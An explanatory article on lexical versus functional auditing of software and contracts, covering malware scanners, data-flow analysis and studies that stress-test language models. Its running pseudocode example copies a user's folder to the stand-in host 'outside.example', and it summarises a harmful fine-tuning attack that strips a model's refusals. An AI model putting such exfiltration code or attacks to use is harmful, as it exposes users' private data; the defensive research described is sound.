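# Auditing software and documents by function rather than wording

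## What a lexical audit and a functional audit each look at

Before a program goes into an app store, a post onto a platform or a contract out to customers, it is usually checked for harm by a person, a short script or a language model (software that has learned to read and write from a large amount of text). The checker can look at how the item is worded and at what it does. Most of the time the two agree, so lists of suspicious words are useful. Those lists become unreliable when someone changes the wording without changing what the item does.

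A *lexical audit* assesses a text or program by the words, names and character patterns in it. The simplest form is a *keyword filter*, which flags any item containing a listed word or phrase. A *signature rule* flags any item containing a fixed pattern of text, code or bytes from known harmful items. A *functional audit* assesses a program or document by what it does or brings about. It looks for a *harmful function*, an effect the review is meant to stop, described in terms of who does what to whom, with what, and without whose consent. Reviewers need this detail because they can't check whether a program is "dangerous", but they can check whether its author uses it to copy a user's files to an outside server without the user's agreement.

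Computer scientists have older terms for this contrast, syntax and semantics. *Mind the Gap* (2020), a paper on machine learning in security, defines syntax as the form of the expressions that a language allows and semantics as a mathematical description of a program's possible behaviour, and notes that syntax is much easier to identify. That ease is the main argument for lexical audits. The argument against them is also old. In *Semantics-Aware Malware Detection* (2005), Christodorescu and colleagues complained that pattern-matching virus scanners ignore what the instructions mean. Sabadin, Harding and Kingston (2026) make a similar criticism of content moderation in *Harm Is Behavioural, Moderation Is Lexical*, arguing that its two familiar failures, silencing harmless speech and missing real abuse, both come from relying on surface form.

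### One program under two sets of names

Here is a small harmful program in pseudocode (a sketch of code for human readers):

```
function steal_private_files(folder):
    stolen = read_all(folder)
    send(stolen, "outside.example")
```

And here it is again:

```
function build_wellness_report(folder):
    summary = read_all(folder)
    send(summary, "outside.example")
```

Both versions read the same folder and send its contents to the same address. They differ only in their *identifiers*, the names an author chooses for variables, functions and files. A *function-preserving rewrite* changes wording or structure without changing behaviour.

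Renaming is safe only within limits. The second version keeps the names `read_all` and `send` because they belong to functions defined elsewhere, and changing them would break the program. Shen, Xi and colleagues (2026), who use renaming to study how names affect language models that read code, change only names that the snippet itself defines. They replace every occurrence, then compare the program's structure before and after to confirm that nothing else changed. They also exclude cases where the name itself affects the program's behavior, such as when a program looks something up by name while it runs.

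Now a harmless file, of the sort a security team might keep for testing an alarm:

```
function steal_passwords():
    print("test passed")
```

With an honest wellness report added, the four programs fill a grid.

| | Harmful function | Harmless function |
|---|---|---|
| **Alarming wording** | `steal_private_files` sends the folder to an outside address | `steal_passwords` prints one line |
| **Neutral wording** | `build_wellness_report` sends the folder to an outside address | `build_wellness_report`, honest version, prints a step count |

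A keyword filter that searches for "steal", "stolen" and "passwords" flags both programs in the top row and passes both in the bottom row. The harmful programs are the two in the left-hand column, so the filter gets two programs right and two wrong. Any two cells that match in function or wording, but not both, form a *contrast pair*. Such pairs are the best test of whether an auditor is relying on wording or function.

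The case in the top right cell appears in *Think Before You Code* (2026), a benchmark for models that write code. It includes requests to rename the first parameter of an existing function to "genocide". The renaming doesn't change what the function computes, but a model gets credit for keeping the word out or warning about it, because the offensive word is itself the harm to prevent. A lexical audit is the right tool for that purpose. Whether wording matters depends on the harm reviewers want to prevent, so they need to decide that first.

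A reviewer should not ignore names either. Shen and colleagues cite research in which descriptive names helped programmers find defects faster, and other research in which misleading cues gave programmers a wrong first idea of what the code did. Names are usually good evidence of what a program does, but whoever wrote the program controls them.

The code doesn't show whether the user consented. If the user asked for an off-site backup, the same three lines are a backup tool. The function of a message can also depend on facts outside its text. Sabadin and colleagues give the example of a request to keep chats from a child's mother, which an unknown adult and an older sibling planning a surprise might send for very different purposes. A functional audit therefore needs facts about the setting as well as the item.

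### The same grid for a contract clause

Suppose a twelve-month subscription costs £20 a month, and a clause makes anyone who leaves early pay for the rest of the year. A subscriber who leaves after three months owes £180 for nine months of a service she will not receive. The seller can give that charge a harsh or friendly name.

| | Harmful function | Harmless function |
|---|---|---|
| **Alarming wording** | "Exit penalty: a member who cancels must pay every remaining monthly charge." | "No penalty, forfeiture or termination fee applies to a member who cancels." |
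| **Neutral wording** | "Loyalty completion: on leaving, a member settles the balance of the plan year." | "A member may leave at any time and owes nothing further." |

A filter that searches for "penalty", "forfeiture" and "termination" again splits the grid by row. It flags the clause that promises no fee but misses the £180, which is labelled as loyalty.

Lawyers faced this problem long before software reviewers did. The EU's *Council Directive 93/13/EEC on unfair terms in consumer contracts* (1993) lists suspect terms by their "object or effect". One entry covers terms that require a consumer who fails in an obligation to pay a disproportionately high sum in compensation. Another covers terms that let the seller keep the money of a consumer who withdraws, without owing the consumer equivalent compensation if the seller cancels. A term can fall under either entry whatever words it uses.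 The list is only indicative, and the assessment must consider the goods or services, the circumstances at signing and the other terms of the contract, so here too part of the function lies outside the words under review. English law on penalty clauses is similar. In *Cavendish Square Holding BV v Talal El Makdessi* (2015), the UK Supreme Court held that classification depends on a term's substance, not its form or the parties' label for it.

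But the same judgment contains an exception. If a contract obliges someone to perform an act and sets a sum payable for failing to, that sum can be a penalty. If the contract imposes no such obligation and provides only that a party who does not perform the act will pay the sum, it cannot be a penalty, even though the same money may change hands on the same event. The judges wrote of "capricious consequences", which the rule about substance reduces. Some wording in a legal document therefore affects how the document operates, much as a name does in a program that looks things up by name, and a reviewer has to know which words are only labels and which have an effect.

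Wording can also affect consent. In 2024 US authorities brought a complaint against the software company Adobe over the early termination fee in its "annual paid monthly" plan. The fee was generally half of the remaining monthly payments, according to the regulator's account in HotHardware's *Adobe To Pay $150 Million To Settle Lawsuit Over Deceptive Subscription Fees*. The complaint focused on disclosure, alleging that Adobe obscured the fee with fine print and hyperlinks and obstructed cancellation. Verdict's *Adobe agrees $150m DOJ settlement over subscription cancellation terms* put the settlement at $75m in civil penalties and $75m in free services, subject to court approval, with Adobe denying wrongdoing. A plain heading in the right place might remove the harm if it is defined as "the seller charges a fee that the customer did not knowingly accept", but not if it is defined as "the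 seller takes a sum out of proportion to the customer's default". The grid above uses the second definition.

### The requirement, stated exactly

Let B(P) be the set of observable effects of a program P over its inputs and environments: what it reads, writes, sends and prints, for each input and each state of the world around it. Let V(P) be the auditor's verdict, flag or pass. A functional auditor then satisfies

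if B(P) = B(P′), then V(P) = V(P′),

and can give different verdicts when the effects differ. The second half is there because an auditor that flags everything satisfies the first half perfectly. Taken together, they mean that the verdict depends on the program only through its effects, with the facts about consent held fixed.

The keyword filter wrongly gives different verdicts to `steal_private_files` and the harmful `build_wellness_report`, which have the same effects. It also fails to distinguish the harmful `build_wellness_report` from the honest one, which has different effects, because neither contains a listed word.

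Adding "send" to the list would catch the disguised program, but it would also flag every mail client and chat application. Sabadin and colleagues measured this tradeoff on English test sentences. Some were hateful but contained no slurs or profanity, and others were harmless but superficially resembled hate speech. Their keyword filter, which left out very common words, missed 60.7% of the hateful sentences and flagged 52.7% of the harmless ones. When the filter included the common words, it missed 45.7% of the hateful sentences and flagged 70.2% of the harmless ones.

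The formal treatment of the requirement comes from virus detection. *A Semantics-Based Approach to Malware Detection* (Dalla Preda, Christodorescu and colleagues, 2008) treats a detector as a function that takes a program and a known piece of malware and returns 1 if the program contains the malware or a disguised variant, and 0 otherwise. A rewrite, such as renaming variables, is a function from programs to programs. A detector is *complete* for a rewrite if it catches every program that contains the rewritten malware, and *sound* if it never flags a program that does not. To capture behaviour, the paper describes each program by its execution traces, the sequences of states it can pass through, then discards the commands and keeps their effects on memory and variables. A program contains the malware if some part of it can reproduce the malware's effects.

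Within that framework they prove that signature matching is generally sound but not complete, meaning that it seldom flags harmless programs but misses rewritten malware. The filter in the grid is neither sound nor complete. The word "steal" can appear anywhere, whereas a long sequence of instructions from a known virus rarely appears in harmless code.

Strict equality of effects is too narrow a test in practice. A version of the wellness program that sends the folder in two halves has different effects from one that sends it whole, but it harms the same victim. Dalla Preda and colleagues ask only for equivalence "up to some notion of equivalence", and add a step that discards what the rewrite changed and keeps the malicious part. Someone has to choose what to discard. Discarding too little lets rewrites escape detection, and discarding too much makes innocent programs match. *Detecting Functional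 Memorization in Code Language Models* (2026), which concerns models that reproduce code from their training data, adds that functional equivalence is a matter of degree, and that a copy that follows only some of the original's execution paths may still carry over what matters, even if most outputs differ. No procedure can settle B(P) for every program, so working auditors approximate it.

The difference between a lexical and a functional audit matters more for generated output, because a language model can reword a program or a clause a hundred times for very little money. It also produces more than people can read, so an automatic check is often the only review an item gets.

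### Four measures of an auditor

The *miss rate* is the share of harmful items an auditor passes. The *false-alarm rate* is the share of harmless items it flags. *Precision* is the share of flagged items that are harmful. On the software grid, the keyword filter misses one of the two harmful programs and flags one of the two harmless ones. One of its two flags is therefore correct, and all three measures are 50%.

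Many papers report *sensitivity* and *specificity* instead, which are 100% minus the miss rate and 100% minus the false-alarm rate. *Auditable Release Control for Pedagogical Leakage in LLM Tutors* (2026) does so for checkers that should stop an AI tutor from giving answers away. Converted, with precision worked out from the 100 leaking and 100 clean replies in each test set, its figures are these:

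| Checker and test set | Miss rate | False-alarm rate | Precision |
|---|---|---|---|
| Lexical checker, first set | 60% | 80% | 33% |
| Lexical checker after revision, first set | 0% | 0% | 100% |
| Lexical checker after revision, fresh set | 100% | 3% | 0% |
| Semantic verifier, first set | 0% | 17% | 85% |
| Semantic verifier, fresh set | 17% | 4% | 95% |

The second and third rows matter most. The researchers revised the rules until they fitted the first set, so the perfect score there was no evidence of how the rules would do on the next one. The 3% in the third row doesn't show by itself that the auditor works, because an auditor that flags nothing gets 0%. The last two rows are somewhat weaker evidence, because the researchers wrote and labelled both sets themselves and designed the meaning-based verifier after the lexical checker had failed on them.

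Precision also depends on how common harm is. Half of the replies in these sets leaked. If only 1 reply in 100 leaked, the semantic verifier, at its fresh-set rates, would catch 83 of the 100 leaks in 10,000 replies and flag 396 of the 9,900 clean replies. Precision would drop from 95% to about 17%, and a reviewer would spend most of their time on clean replies.

Some auditors give each item a score rather than a verdict, and the reviewer chooses the threshold above which items are flagged. A lower threshold means fewer misses and more false alarms. The *ROC curve* plots the share of harmful items caught against the false-alarm rate at every threshold. The *area under the curve*, or AUC, is the chance that a randomly chosen harmful item scores above a randomly chosen harmless one, with ties counting half. A perfect ranking has an AUC of 1, and guessing gives 0.5.

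The AUC for the software grid can be calculated by hand. Each program's score is the number of different listed words it contains, which is 2 for `steal_private_files`, 2 for `steal_passwords`, and 0 for each wellness report. Of the four possible pairs of a harmful and a harmless program, one is in the right order, one is in the wrong order, and two are ties. Counting each tie as half, the total is 2 out of 4. The AUC is therefore 0.5, and no threshold makes the filter better than chance.

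For an auditor that gives only verdicts, the corresponding measure is *balanced accuracy*, the average of sensitivity and specificity. The English keyword filter of Sabadin and colleagues scores 0.43, slightly worse than a coin flip, while individual human annotators reached 0.99 on the same sentences. The test is deliberately hard, with harmless sentences included because they resemble hateful ones. On everyday messages the filter would raise fewer false alarms, but it would be no better at detecting hatred that uses none of the listed words.

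## How keyword filters and signature rules work, and how they err

The keyword filter in the example grid checked only whether a program contained one of three words. Most filters in use do more, and each extra step removes one kind of mistake but can introduce another.

### A keyword filter, step by step

A filter first *normalises* the text, removing differences that its designer considers irrelevant. It usually converts capitals to lowercase, so that "STEAL" and "steal" count as the same word. It then splits the text into *tokens*, the units it will compare with its list. In English prose, these are mostly words separated by spaces and punctuation. Code is harder to split because programmers join words. A filter that splits only at spaces and punctuation may treat `steal_private_files` as one unknown word, so it must also split at underscores. It can split `stealPrivateFiles` at the capitals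 only if it does so before converting them to lowercase.

The filter next compares the tokens with its list. An entry can be a plain word or a *regular expression*, a pattern that matches a set of strings. For example, `steal(s|ing)?` matches "steal", "steals" and "stealing". The crudest filters flag an item on any match. Others give each entry a weight, add up the weights of the entries they find, and flag the item if the total reaches a threshold.

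Suppose "steal" and "stolen" weigh 3 each, "passwords" weighs 2, "send" weighs 1, and the threshold is 3. The openly named thief, `steal_private_files`, scores 7. The harmless alarm test, `steal_passwords`, scores 5. The disguised thief, `build_wellness_report`, scores 1, and its honest namesake scores 0. As before, the filter flags the harmless test and misses the disguised thief. The disguised thief's one point is still somewhat informative, because "send" is the one listed word that the author couldn't rename without breaking the program. Filters work better when they look for things the author isn't free to change.

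### Signature rules for code

Signature rules try to use such things. Malware analysts often write them in YARA, a pattern-matching tool. According to YARA's documentation, a rule can define text strings, regular expressions and hexadecimal strings (raw bytes), and its condition is a true-or-false expression that usually refers to them. Here is a rule for the grid:

```
rule example_thief
{
    strings:
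        $word = "steal" nocase
        $address = "outside.example"
    condition:
        $word or $address
}
```

The modifier `nocase` makes the match ignore capitalization. This rule flags the two harmful programs and the harmless test. With `and` in place of `or`, it flags only the openly named file-stealing program. With `$address` alone, it flags only the two harmful programs, since both must contain the address they send the files to.

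Semgrep, another pattern-matching tool, works on the parsed structure of source code, so spacing and comments make no difference. Its patterns can contain placeholders, marked with a dollar sign, that stand for any name. Adapted to the pseudocode, a pattern for the grid might be:

```
$DATA = read_all(...)
...
send($DATA, ...)
```

A rule can match any program that stores what it has read under some name and later sends whatever has that name. Datadog Security Labs published a simplified rule of this kind for real Python packages. It matches code that takes the computer's network name, or the access keys to an Amazon cloud account, and passes them to a function that makes web requests. The rule doesn't depend on variable names, and it uses Semgrep's tracing mode, a form of data-flow analysis, so it is partly a functional audit.

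| Program | Weighted filter | YARA, "steal" only | YARA, address only | Semgrep pattern |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| `steal_private_files` (harmful) | 7, flag | flag | flag | flag |
| `build_wellness_report` (harmful) | 1, pass | pass | flag | flag |
| `steal_passwords` (harmless) | 5, flag | flag | pass | pass |
| `build_wellness_report` (honest) | 0, pass | pass | pass | pass |

The last two columns have no errors, but it is easy to write a rule that sorts four programs you have already seen. The address rule misses the same data-stealing program if its address changes, and it flags a security product that lists the address to block it. The Semgrep pattern flags a legitimate backup tool and misses a data-stealing program that reads files with a different function.

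Regular expressions can be too broad in less obvious ways. Portland State University course notes on YARA include a pattern for IP addresses that looks for four groups of up to three digits, separated by dots. A version number such as 4.8.1.0 also matches.

### A refusal that scores worse than a dangerous answer

Some filters skip tokens altogether and search for listed words anywhere in the text, including inside longer words. Akram, Yenugu and colleagues (2026), in *Safer Content or Firmer Refusals?*, used a filter of this kind to score chatbot replies, and they describe its faults frankly in an appendix. They were testing ways to protect a language model against harmful fine-tuning, further training on bad examples that makes a model stop refusing dangerous requests. Their list had 31 words, among them "kill", "harm", "illegal", "drug" and "address", and the score for a reply r was

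Harm(r) = min(100, 10 × number of different listed words found in r).

Under this rule "harm" fires on "harmless" and "drug" fires on "drugstore". The same list would find "kill" in "skill" and "stab" in "establish".

In their most telling example, a model politely says that it cannot address a request because the information would be harmful and illegal. This refusal scores 30 because it contains "address", "harm" and "illegal", while a dangerous answer that uses none of the listed words scores 0. Matching only whole words would help a little, since "harm" would no longer match "harmful", but the refusal would still score 20 and the dangerous answer 0. The larger problem is that people and chatbots use words like these when they warn against harm, while someone giving practical instructions may not need them.

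This affected the results. Before the attack, all three protected versions of the model refused all ten test requests, and their average harm scores were 24, 26 and 27. After the attack, which trained them on 500 harmful examples, they refused 20%, 30% and 50% of the requests, and their harm scores were 20, 26 and 19. A reader with only the harm scores would conclude that the attack had done nothing, or had made the models slightly safer. The small drops may be due to chance, because the experiment used only ten requests and one run per version, and when the researchers repeated one version, its score before the attack was 32 instead of 24. But harm scores should rise when a model stops refusing at least half of the dangerous requests, and these didn't. Akram and colleagues instead used the score from a separate moderation service as their main measure of content safety.

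### Why longer lists raise false alarms

Filters miss harmful items that contain none of the listed terms. If a filter flags every item with at least one match, adding a term can flag more items but never fewer, so it can lower the miss rate but may also raise the false-alarm rate. Sabadin and colleagues saw this tradeoff when they added common words to their filter.

False alarms accumulate quickly even if each rule seldom misfires. Let q be the chance that a harmless program matches any one rule, and let k be the number of rules. If the matches are independent, the chance of at least one false alarm is

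1 − (1 − q)^k.

If 50 rules each misfire on 2% of harmless programs, independently of one another, about 64% of those programs will be flagged by at least one rule. Real rules tend to misfire on the same programs, which lowers the figure, but it still rises as rules are added.

Something close to the worst case happened at the Python Package Index (PyPI), the public library from which programmers install Python code. As Chainguard's *Taming bad Python packages* describes it, one of PyPI's security checks ran YARA rules over `setup.py`, a file that controls a package's installation. Guo, Liu and colleagues (2026), in *Cutting the Gordian Knot*, ran PyPI's rules and three other rule-based scanners on 18,137 packages, roughly half of them malicious. Their counts give these approximate rates:

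| Scanner | Harmless packages flagged | Malicious packages missed | Places flagged in the code |
|---|---|---|---|
| PyPI's own check | 88% | 2% | 248,737 |
| OSSGadget | 85% | 12% | 4,955,383 |
| Bandit4Mal | 80% | 54% | 695,974 |
| GuardDog | 5% | 10% | 11,420 |

Guo and colleagues report that, in a separate test set, PyPI's rules flagged 97% of packages for "metaprogramming", code that manipulates other code, when the packages only used standard Python imports, the lines that load libraries in almost every program. The 97% is probably a share of the wrongly flagged packages, because the paper's counts show that the rules flagged about 88% of all harmless packages. One file set off 31,242 alerts.

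The check's low miss rate is not very impressive given how many false alarms it raised. Bandit4Mal did even worse, flagging most of the harmless packages and missing more than half of the malicious ones. One of its rules flagged any web address, including links to a project's home page and documentation, and matching more harmless text like this doesn't reduce misses.

Guo and colleagues chose popular harmless packages, which set off more alerts than randomly chosen ones, so everyday false-alarm rates would probably be lower, but they would have to be far lower to be workable. In *One Detector Fits All* (2025), researchers tuned a detector to a false-alarm rate of 0.1% and ran it on 91,949 PyPI packages over 37 days, which left about two false alarms a day to check. A false-alarm rate of 88% would produce nearly 2,200 a day from the same packages.

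Chainguard's *hunting malware on package repositories* reports that requiring more alerts before flagging a package made scanners miss nearly all malicious packages before the number of results became manageable. Harmless packages can set off many alerts, up to 145,799 for a single package in that study. Choosing better rules helped more. Networking code in unexpected places was a good sign of malice, while metaprogramming and running outside programs were less useful signs.

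Two packages that Guo and colleagues examined show why many of these rules err. The harmless `gen_wrappers` fetches an image from a program on the same computer and encodes it. The malicious `gmgeoip` reads a system file that lists user accounts, encodes it and sends it to an outside address. Both use the same standard functions to encode data and build web requests. Bandit4Mal, OSSGadget and GuardDog all flagged `gen_wrappers`. The packages differ in what data they read and where that data goes, but a rule that matches single function calls can't detect either difference.

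The harmless alarm test in the grid also has real counterparts. *MalGuard* (2025) describes a detector that learns from examples instead of following hand-written rules. It flagged 144 recently uploaded PyPI packages, 31 of which were not malicious. Twenty-five of the 31 were harmless test demos that made web requests or launched other programs, and the other six were pranks.

### When the word is the harm

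A lexical check is the right tool when the offensive word is itself the harm, as in the request to name a parameter "genocide". Researchers at Concordia University in Montreal have twice studied whether language models put such words into code when asked.

In *Automated Harmfulness Testing for Code Large Language Models*, Tan, Wang and colleagues (2025) examined 66 refactorings, which are standard rewrites that preserve a program's function. They found 32 that could introduce an offensive word into a harmless program, combined them with 100 words and phrases from 13 categories of harm, and sent the requests to five small models, all since superseded. On average, the models wrote the word without a warning in 65.93% of replies, left it out with a warning in 7.49%, and gave neither the word nor a warning in 25.98%. Code Llama, Meta's coding model, had the lowest rate of the five for writing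 the word without a warning, at 38.13%, but this may not reflect caution. Nearly half of its replies contained neither the word nor a warning, and the researchers found that it tended to explain the code when it couldn't manage a complex change.

The models objected more often to ordinary prose, declining with a warning in 20.46% of replies when asked to insert the word as a comment. When phrases were run together like program names, the models wrote them without warning 73.22% of the time, compared with 64.10% for single words.

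Tan and colleagues sorted the replies by using regular expressions to find the code and check it for the injected word. They detected warnings with a keyword list built from reading a fifth of the replies, and chose keywords over more advanced language processing because the check had to run fast. Two people then labelled 1,920 of the remaining replies without seeing the tool's results, and the tool matched their labels 97.55% of the time. A similar technique failed badly as a harm score for chatbot replies. This one worked because the researchers had planted the word themselves, so they knew exactly what to search for, and because its presence was what they wanted to detect.

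The advantage is smaller when nobody has deliberately inserted the word. "Kill" is on Akram and colleagues' list of harmful terms, but it is also the standard Unix command for stopping a running program.

A lexical check also can't show whether the program still works. The second study, *Structured Safety Auditing for Balancing Code Correctness and Content Safety* (Tan, Wang and Tan, 2026), treats code as two channels, one that the machine executes and one that people read. The researchers combined each of 591 programming tasks with a request to rename a parameter, using each of five extremely offensive words in turn, for 2,955 requests in total. They then ran each task's tests on the resulting code, checked whether the word appeared in it, and looked for a warning.

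On the smaller of the two task sets, code from OpenAI's GPT-4o-mini passed its tests 71.83% of the time, but only 2.20% of its replies were both correct and free of the word. Asking the model to think step by step raised that share to 6.59%, and a reminder about safety raised it to 23.05%. The best method made the model write down any problem with the wording, and then what the function had to do, before writing code. This raised the share to 64.02% and the pass rate to 87.07%.

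The same method produced a very different result with CodeGemma, a small Google model. Its average damage score on the lexical check fell to 0.03, on a scale from 0 to 2 where 2 means that the model repeats the offensive word without warning. But only 4.27% of its replies passed the tests, because most of them contained no code at all. The lexical check was right about the offensive word, but it took the tests to show that the model had mostly stopped writing code.

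### What filters do well

Filters have practical advantages even when a word is only a clue. Comparing text with a list takes very little computing, and the reviewer doesn't have to run the program or pay for a language model. A fixed rule always gives the same verdict on the same text. The verdict is also easy to explain. The scanners that Guo and colleagues tested report the file, the line and the pattern that matched, so an author who disputes a flag can see what caused it.

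Filters work best on exact strings from known attacks, such as the web address of a malicious server or a file's *hash*, a short fingerprint calculated from its contents. Changing a single byte changes the hash, so a hash rule almost never flags a harmless file, but it catches only exact copies.

Exact copies are common, though. Guo and colleagues extracted only 2,283 different pieces of malicious code from 8,543 malicious packages, because attackers often release batches of packages containing the same code. A signature taken from the first package in a batch can catch the others, even if their names and descriptions differ.

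### Can updates keep up?

Reviewers can update a filter's list whenever authors change their wording. This works well for hashes and server addresses, where a new entry takes little work and rarely affects anyone else. Broader rules need more upkeep. GuardDog, the most precise scanner in the table above, missed 5.6% of malicious packages in Guo and colleagues' main test set and 31.9% in a set of newer ones. The two sets came from different sources, so age may not explain the whole increase.

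Coded language is harder to keep up with. In *New Terms, New Toxicity*, Cui, Zhang and colleagues (2026) collected 974 Chinese terms that look harmless but have acquired an abusive or illicit meaning. "Android" can be an insult for people of low status, and "open the box" can mean publishing someone's private details. They tested five commercial moderation services on 490 harmful sentences containing such terms. The services caught between 0% and 26% of the sentences, even though they are not simple word lists.

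Cui and colleagues say that the terms' meanings change rapidly, but they don't measure the rate. About half of their test sentences used terms outside the knowledge of Qwen2.5-7B, a small language model from 2024. This is weak evidence of turnover, since a small model may lack older terms too.

Their procedure for building the list shows why a careful list lags behind usage. They accepted a term only if the first page of search results already showed its harmful meaning, and then had people review it in two rounds. This test keeps the list from filling up with words that hardly anyone uses abusively, but it also means that a term gets onto the list only after its harmful meaning has spread.

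Even an up-to-date list would handle "Android" badly, because an entry meant to catch the insult would also flag every conversation about Android phones. Cui and colleagues instead trained a small language model to look up unfamiliar terms on the web and use the results to judge each sentence. It caught 92.86% of the harmful sentences, and its overall accuracy implies that it wrongly flagged only about 2 of the 134 harmless sentences that also contained new terms. Some of its training examples came from the same collection of terms as the test, which probably helped it. But adding entries to a list couldn't keep false alarms this low, because each entry also flags the word's harmless uses.

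## Following data and control through the code

To tell packages like `gen_wrappers` and `gmgeoip` apart, a reviewer has to know what data each one reads and where it sends that data. The reviewer can often work this out through *static analysis*, which means examining the code without running it. The most relevant form here is *data-flow analysis*, or taint tracking, which traces where data comes from and where it can end up.

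### From text to a path

The analyser first parses the code into a *syntax tree*, a diagram of which parts of the program sit inside which others. `steal_private_files` becomes a function with one parameter and two statements. The first statement stores the result of a call to `read_all` in a variable. The second calls `send` with that variable and a fixed piece of text. The harmful `build_wellness_report` has the same tree with different labels.

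The analyser then works out which labels refer to the same thing and replaces every name that the program itself defines with a placeholder:

```
function F1(V1):
    V2 = read_all(V1)
    send(V2, "outside.example")
```

Both harmful programs turn into exactly this text, so no later step can depend on whether the author wrote "stolen" or "summary".

The *control-flow graph* records the order in which statements can run. In this program the second line always runs before the third. Putting `if user_agreed():` in front of `send` would split the graph into one branch that sends the files and one that doesn't.

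The *data-flow graph* connects each statement that sets a variable to the later statements that use that value. Here it connects the second line to the third, because the second sets V2 and the third uses it. If the program ran `V2 = "hello"` in between, that connection would disappear, and the contents of the files would no longer reach `send`. A keyword filter would find the same words in both versions.

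The reviewer marks *sources*, where sensitive data enters, and *sinks*, where it could do harm. To look for code that steals files, the reviewer marks the result of `read_all` as a source and the first argument of `send` as a sink. The analyser then searches for a path from the source to the sink.

| Program | Path from source to sink |
|---|---|
| `steal_private_files` (harmful) | `read_all` → `stolen` → `send` |
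| `build_wellness_report` (harmful) | `read_all` → `summary` → `send` |
| Either of these, with placeholders | `read_all` → V2 → `send` |
| `steal_passwords` (harmless) | none |
| `build_wellness_report` (honest) | none |

The Semgrep pattern in the previous section also sorted these four programs correctly, but it needs the same variable to appear in both calls. A slightly longer version of the harmful program doesn't meet that condition:

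```
function build_wellness_report(folder):
    summary = read_all(folder)
    page = "Report: " + summary
    deliver(page)

function deliver(item):
    send(item, "outside.example")
```

A data-flow analyser still finds the path from `summary` to `page` to `item` to `send`. To do so, it also has to follow values computed from the marked data, such as a longer text that contains it, and follow data from one function into another.

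Most research uses this method to look for *vulnerabilities*, mistakes that outsiders can exploit in programs written in good faith. The source is then anything an outsider can type in, and the sink is an operation such as running a system command. The reviewer can also mark *barriers*, checks that make the data safe, and the analyser stops tracking the data there. In the wellness program, a reviewer might treat `user_agreed` as a barrier, but only after confirming that the function asks the user, because an author could give that name to a function that always returns true.

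The graph can contain paths that the data never takes. For example, the condition in front of `send` might never be true, and no method can decide this for every program (a consequence of Rice's theorem). Analysers therefore usually assume that either branch can run, which produces some false alarms.

### Names that have to stay

Placeholders cause trouble when a program looks up its own parts by name while it runs, a feature called *reflection*. Suppose the wellness program contains this line:

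```
call_by_name("build_" + choice)
```

If `choice` is "wellness_report", the program looks up `build_wellness_report` by name and runs it, so renaming that function makes the lookup fail. Changing a name can also break other software. Another program may call the function by its name, or a server may require a field called `step_count` in the data it receives.

Replacing names with placeholders in an analyser's own copy of a program doesn't break the program, but the analyser can lose the connection between the text "build_wellness_report" and the function of that name. It then misses any path that depends on looking up the function by name. Keeping such names helps when they appear in the code, but if the program builds a name from input it receives at run time, static analysis may be unable to tell which function will run.

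The analyser keeps the names `read_all` and `send` for a different reason. Their code is outside the program, so the analyser can identify what they do only by name. Without those names, the harmful program would be reduced to a function that gets a value from one place and passes it to another, which also describes many harmless programs.

Every analyser of this kind therefore contains a word list. Nguyen, Ho and colleagues (2025), in *Leveraging Code Slicing for LLMs-based Malicious NPM Package Detection*, used a list of 256 JavaScript functions, each marked as a source, a sink or both. They adapted it from a list for Python and added functions that appeared in published attacks on npm, the public library of JavaScript packages. A function missing from the list can't start or end a path, so the list needs updating, as a keyword filter does. Unlike a keyword filter, though, the analyser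 raises an alarm only if the right data reaches a listed function.

In one study, removing names and fixed values from syntax trees made language models only slightly less accurate at detecting vulnerable code. Grasso, Liguori and colleagues (2026), in *Enhancing LLM-Based Vulnerability Detection via Representation-Aware Logical Ensemble*, trained three small language models to label C functions as vulnerable or safe, using a balanced set in which guessing would be right half the time. The models were right 70% to 71% of the time with complete syntax trees, 67% with trees stripped of every name (including library names) and fixed value, and 70% to 73% with plain source code. Flawfinder, an older scanner that searches C code for risky function names, was right 53% of the time.

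Structure alone thus helped far more than a list of risky names, and adding the names back gained only a few points. But none of these detectors was accurate enough to rely on, and larger models may benefit more from names.

### Templates that describe behaviour

Christodorescu and colleagues brought this way of thinking to virus detection in their 2005 paper on semantics-aware malware detection. In place of a signature made of fixed bytes, they described a malicious behaviour with a *template*, a short series of instructions in which symbols stand for particular variables and values. A template for the running example would look like this:

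```
A = read_all(B)
send(A, C)
```

A program matches if its own variables and values can take the places of A, B and C, and if the value that reaches `send` is still the one that came from `read_all`. The matching instructions can be anywhere in the file, with unrelated instructions between them, as long as they run in the right order. Renaming the variables or rearranging the file therefore doesn't break the match. Machine code has no variable names, so the equivalent of renaming is using a different register, one of the processor's small storage slots.

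Dalla Preda and colleagues later proved that the 2005 detector is complete for several common rewrites, provided that the analyses it relies on, such as the one that builds the control-flow graph, always give correct answers. In practice these analyses make mistakes, and Dalla Preda and colleagues point out that even turning a finished program back into readable instructions can be difficult. If the detector misses a rewrite that the proof covers, the error must come from one of these analyses.

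### Slices for a language model to read

Tracing data also helps a reviewer decide which code to read. A *slice* is the part of a program that can affect a chosen point or be affected by it. If a package has 10,000 lines and five of them steal files, a slice traced backwards from `send` should contain those five and leave out most of the rest. Several recent systems extract such slices and give them to a language model.

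The main advantage of slicing is that it reduces the amount of code a model has to process. The largest package in Nguyen and colleagues' npm collection had 15.8 million *tokens*, the word fragments that language models process, which they say is far more than any current model can handle. Slicing cut the average size from 162,920 tokens to 403. It also discarded mostly the right code, keeping 74% of the lines that used a listed function in malicious packages but only 9% of those in harmless ones.

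DeepSeek-Coder, a small open model, then scored each slice for signs of malice. It missed 27% of the malicious packages, and 96% of its flags were correct. When the researchers chopped the full code into equal pieces instead, the same model missed 44%, and 87% of its flags were correct. (The paper also reports an accuracy of 87% with slices, but its miss rate and precision imply about 83%.)

These figures cover only the packages that produced a slice. The analyser found no path in 44% of the malicious packages that used a listed function. If a reviewer treated every empty slice as a pass, the system would miss about 59% of those malicious packages. Nguyen and colleagues attribute the empty slices mainly to code that hides its purpose or builds further code as it runs, and they recommend sending such packages to a sandbox or unscrambling the code first. Empty slices were even more common among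 harmless packages, at 67%, but for many of those an empty slice may be the correct result.

Nguyen and colleagues didn't test renaming, but Lekssays, Mouhcine and colleagues did in *LLMxCPG* (2025). Their system uses a *code property graph*, which combines the syntax tree, control-flow graph and dependencies between statements. One language model writes a search query for the graph, and a program called Joern runs the query and extracts a slice of the code. A second language model then labels the slice vulnerable or safe. The slices were 68% to 91% smaller than the original code.

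To test the second model, they replaced the names of all function parameters with random ones:

| Test set | Miss rate, original names | Miss rate, random names | Precision, original names | Precision, random names |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| FormAI (programs written by AI) | 19.5% | 19.5% | 81.0% | 81.0% |
| PrimeVul (real code) | 55.0% | 52.5% | 100% | 100% |
| SVEN (real code, not used in training) | 4.7% | 30.2% | 55.9% | 54.9% |

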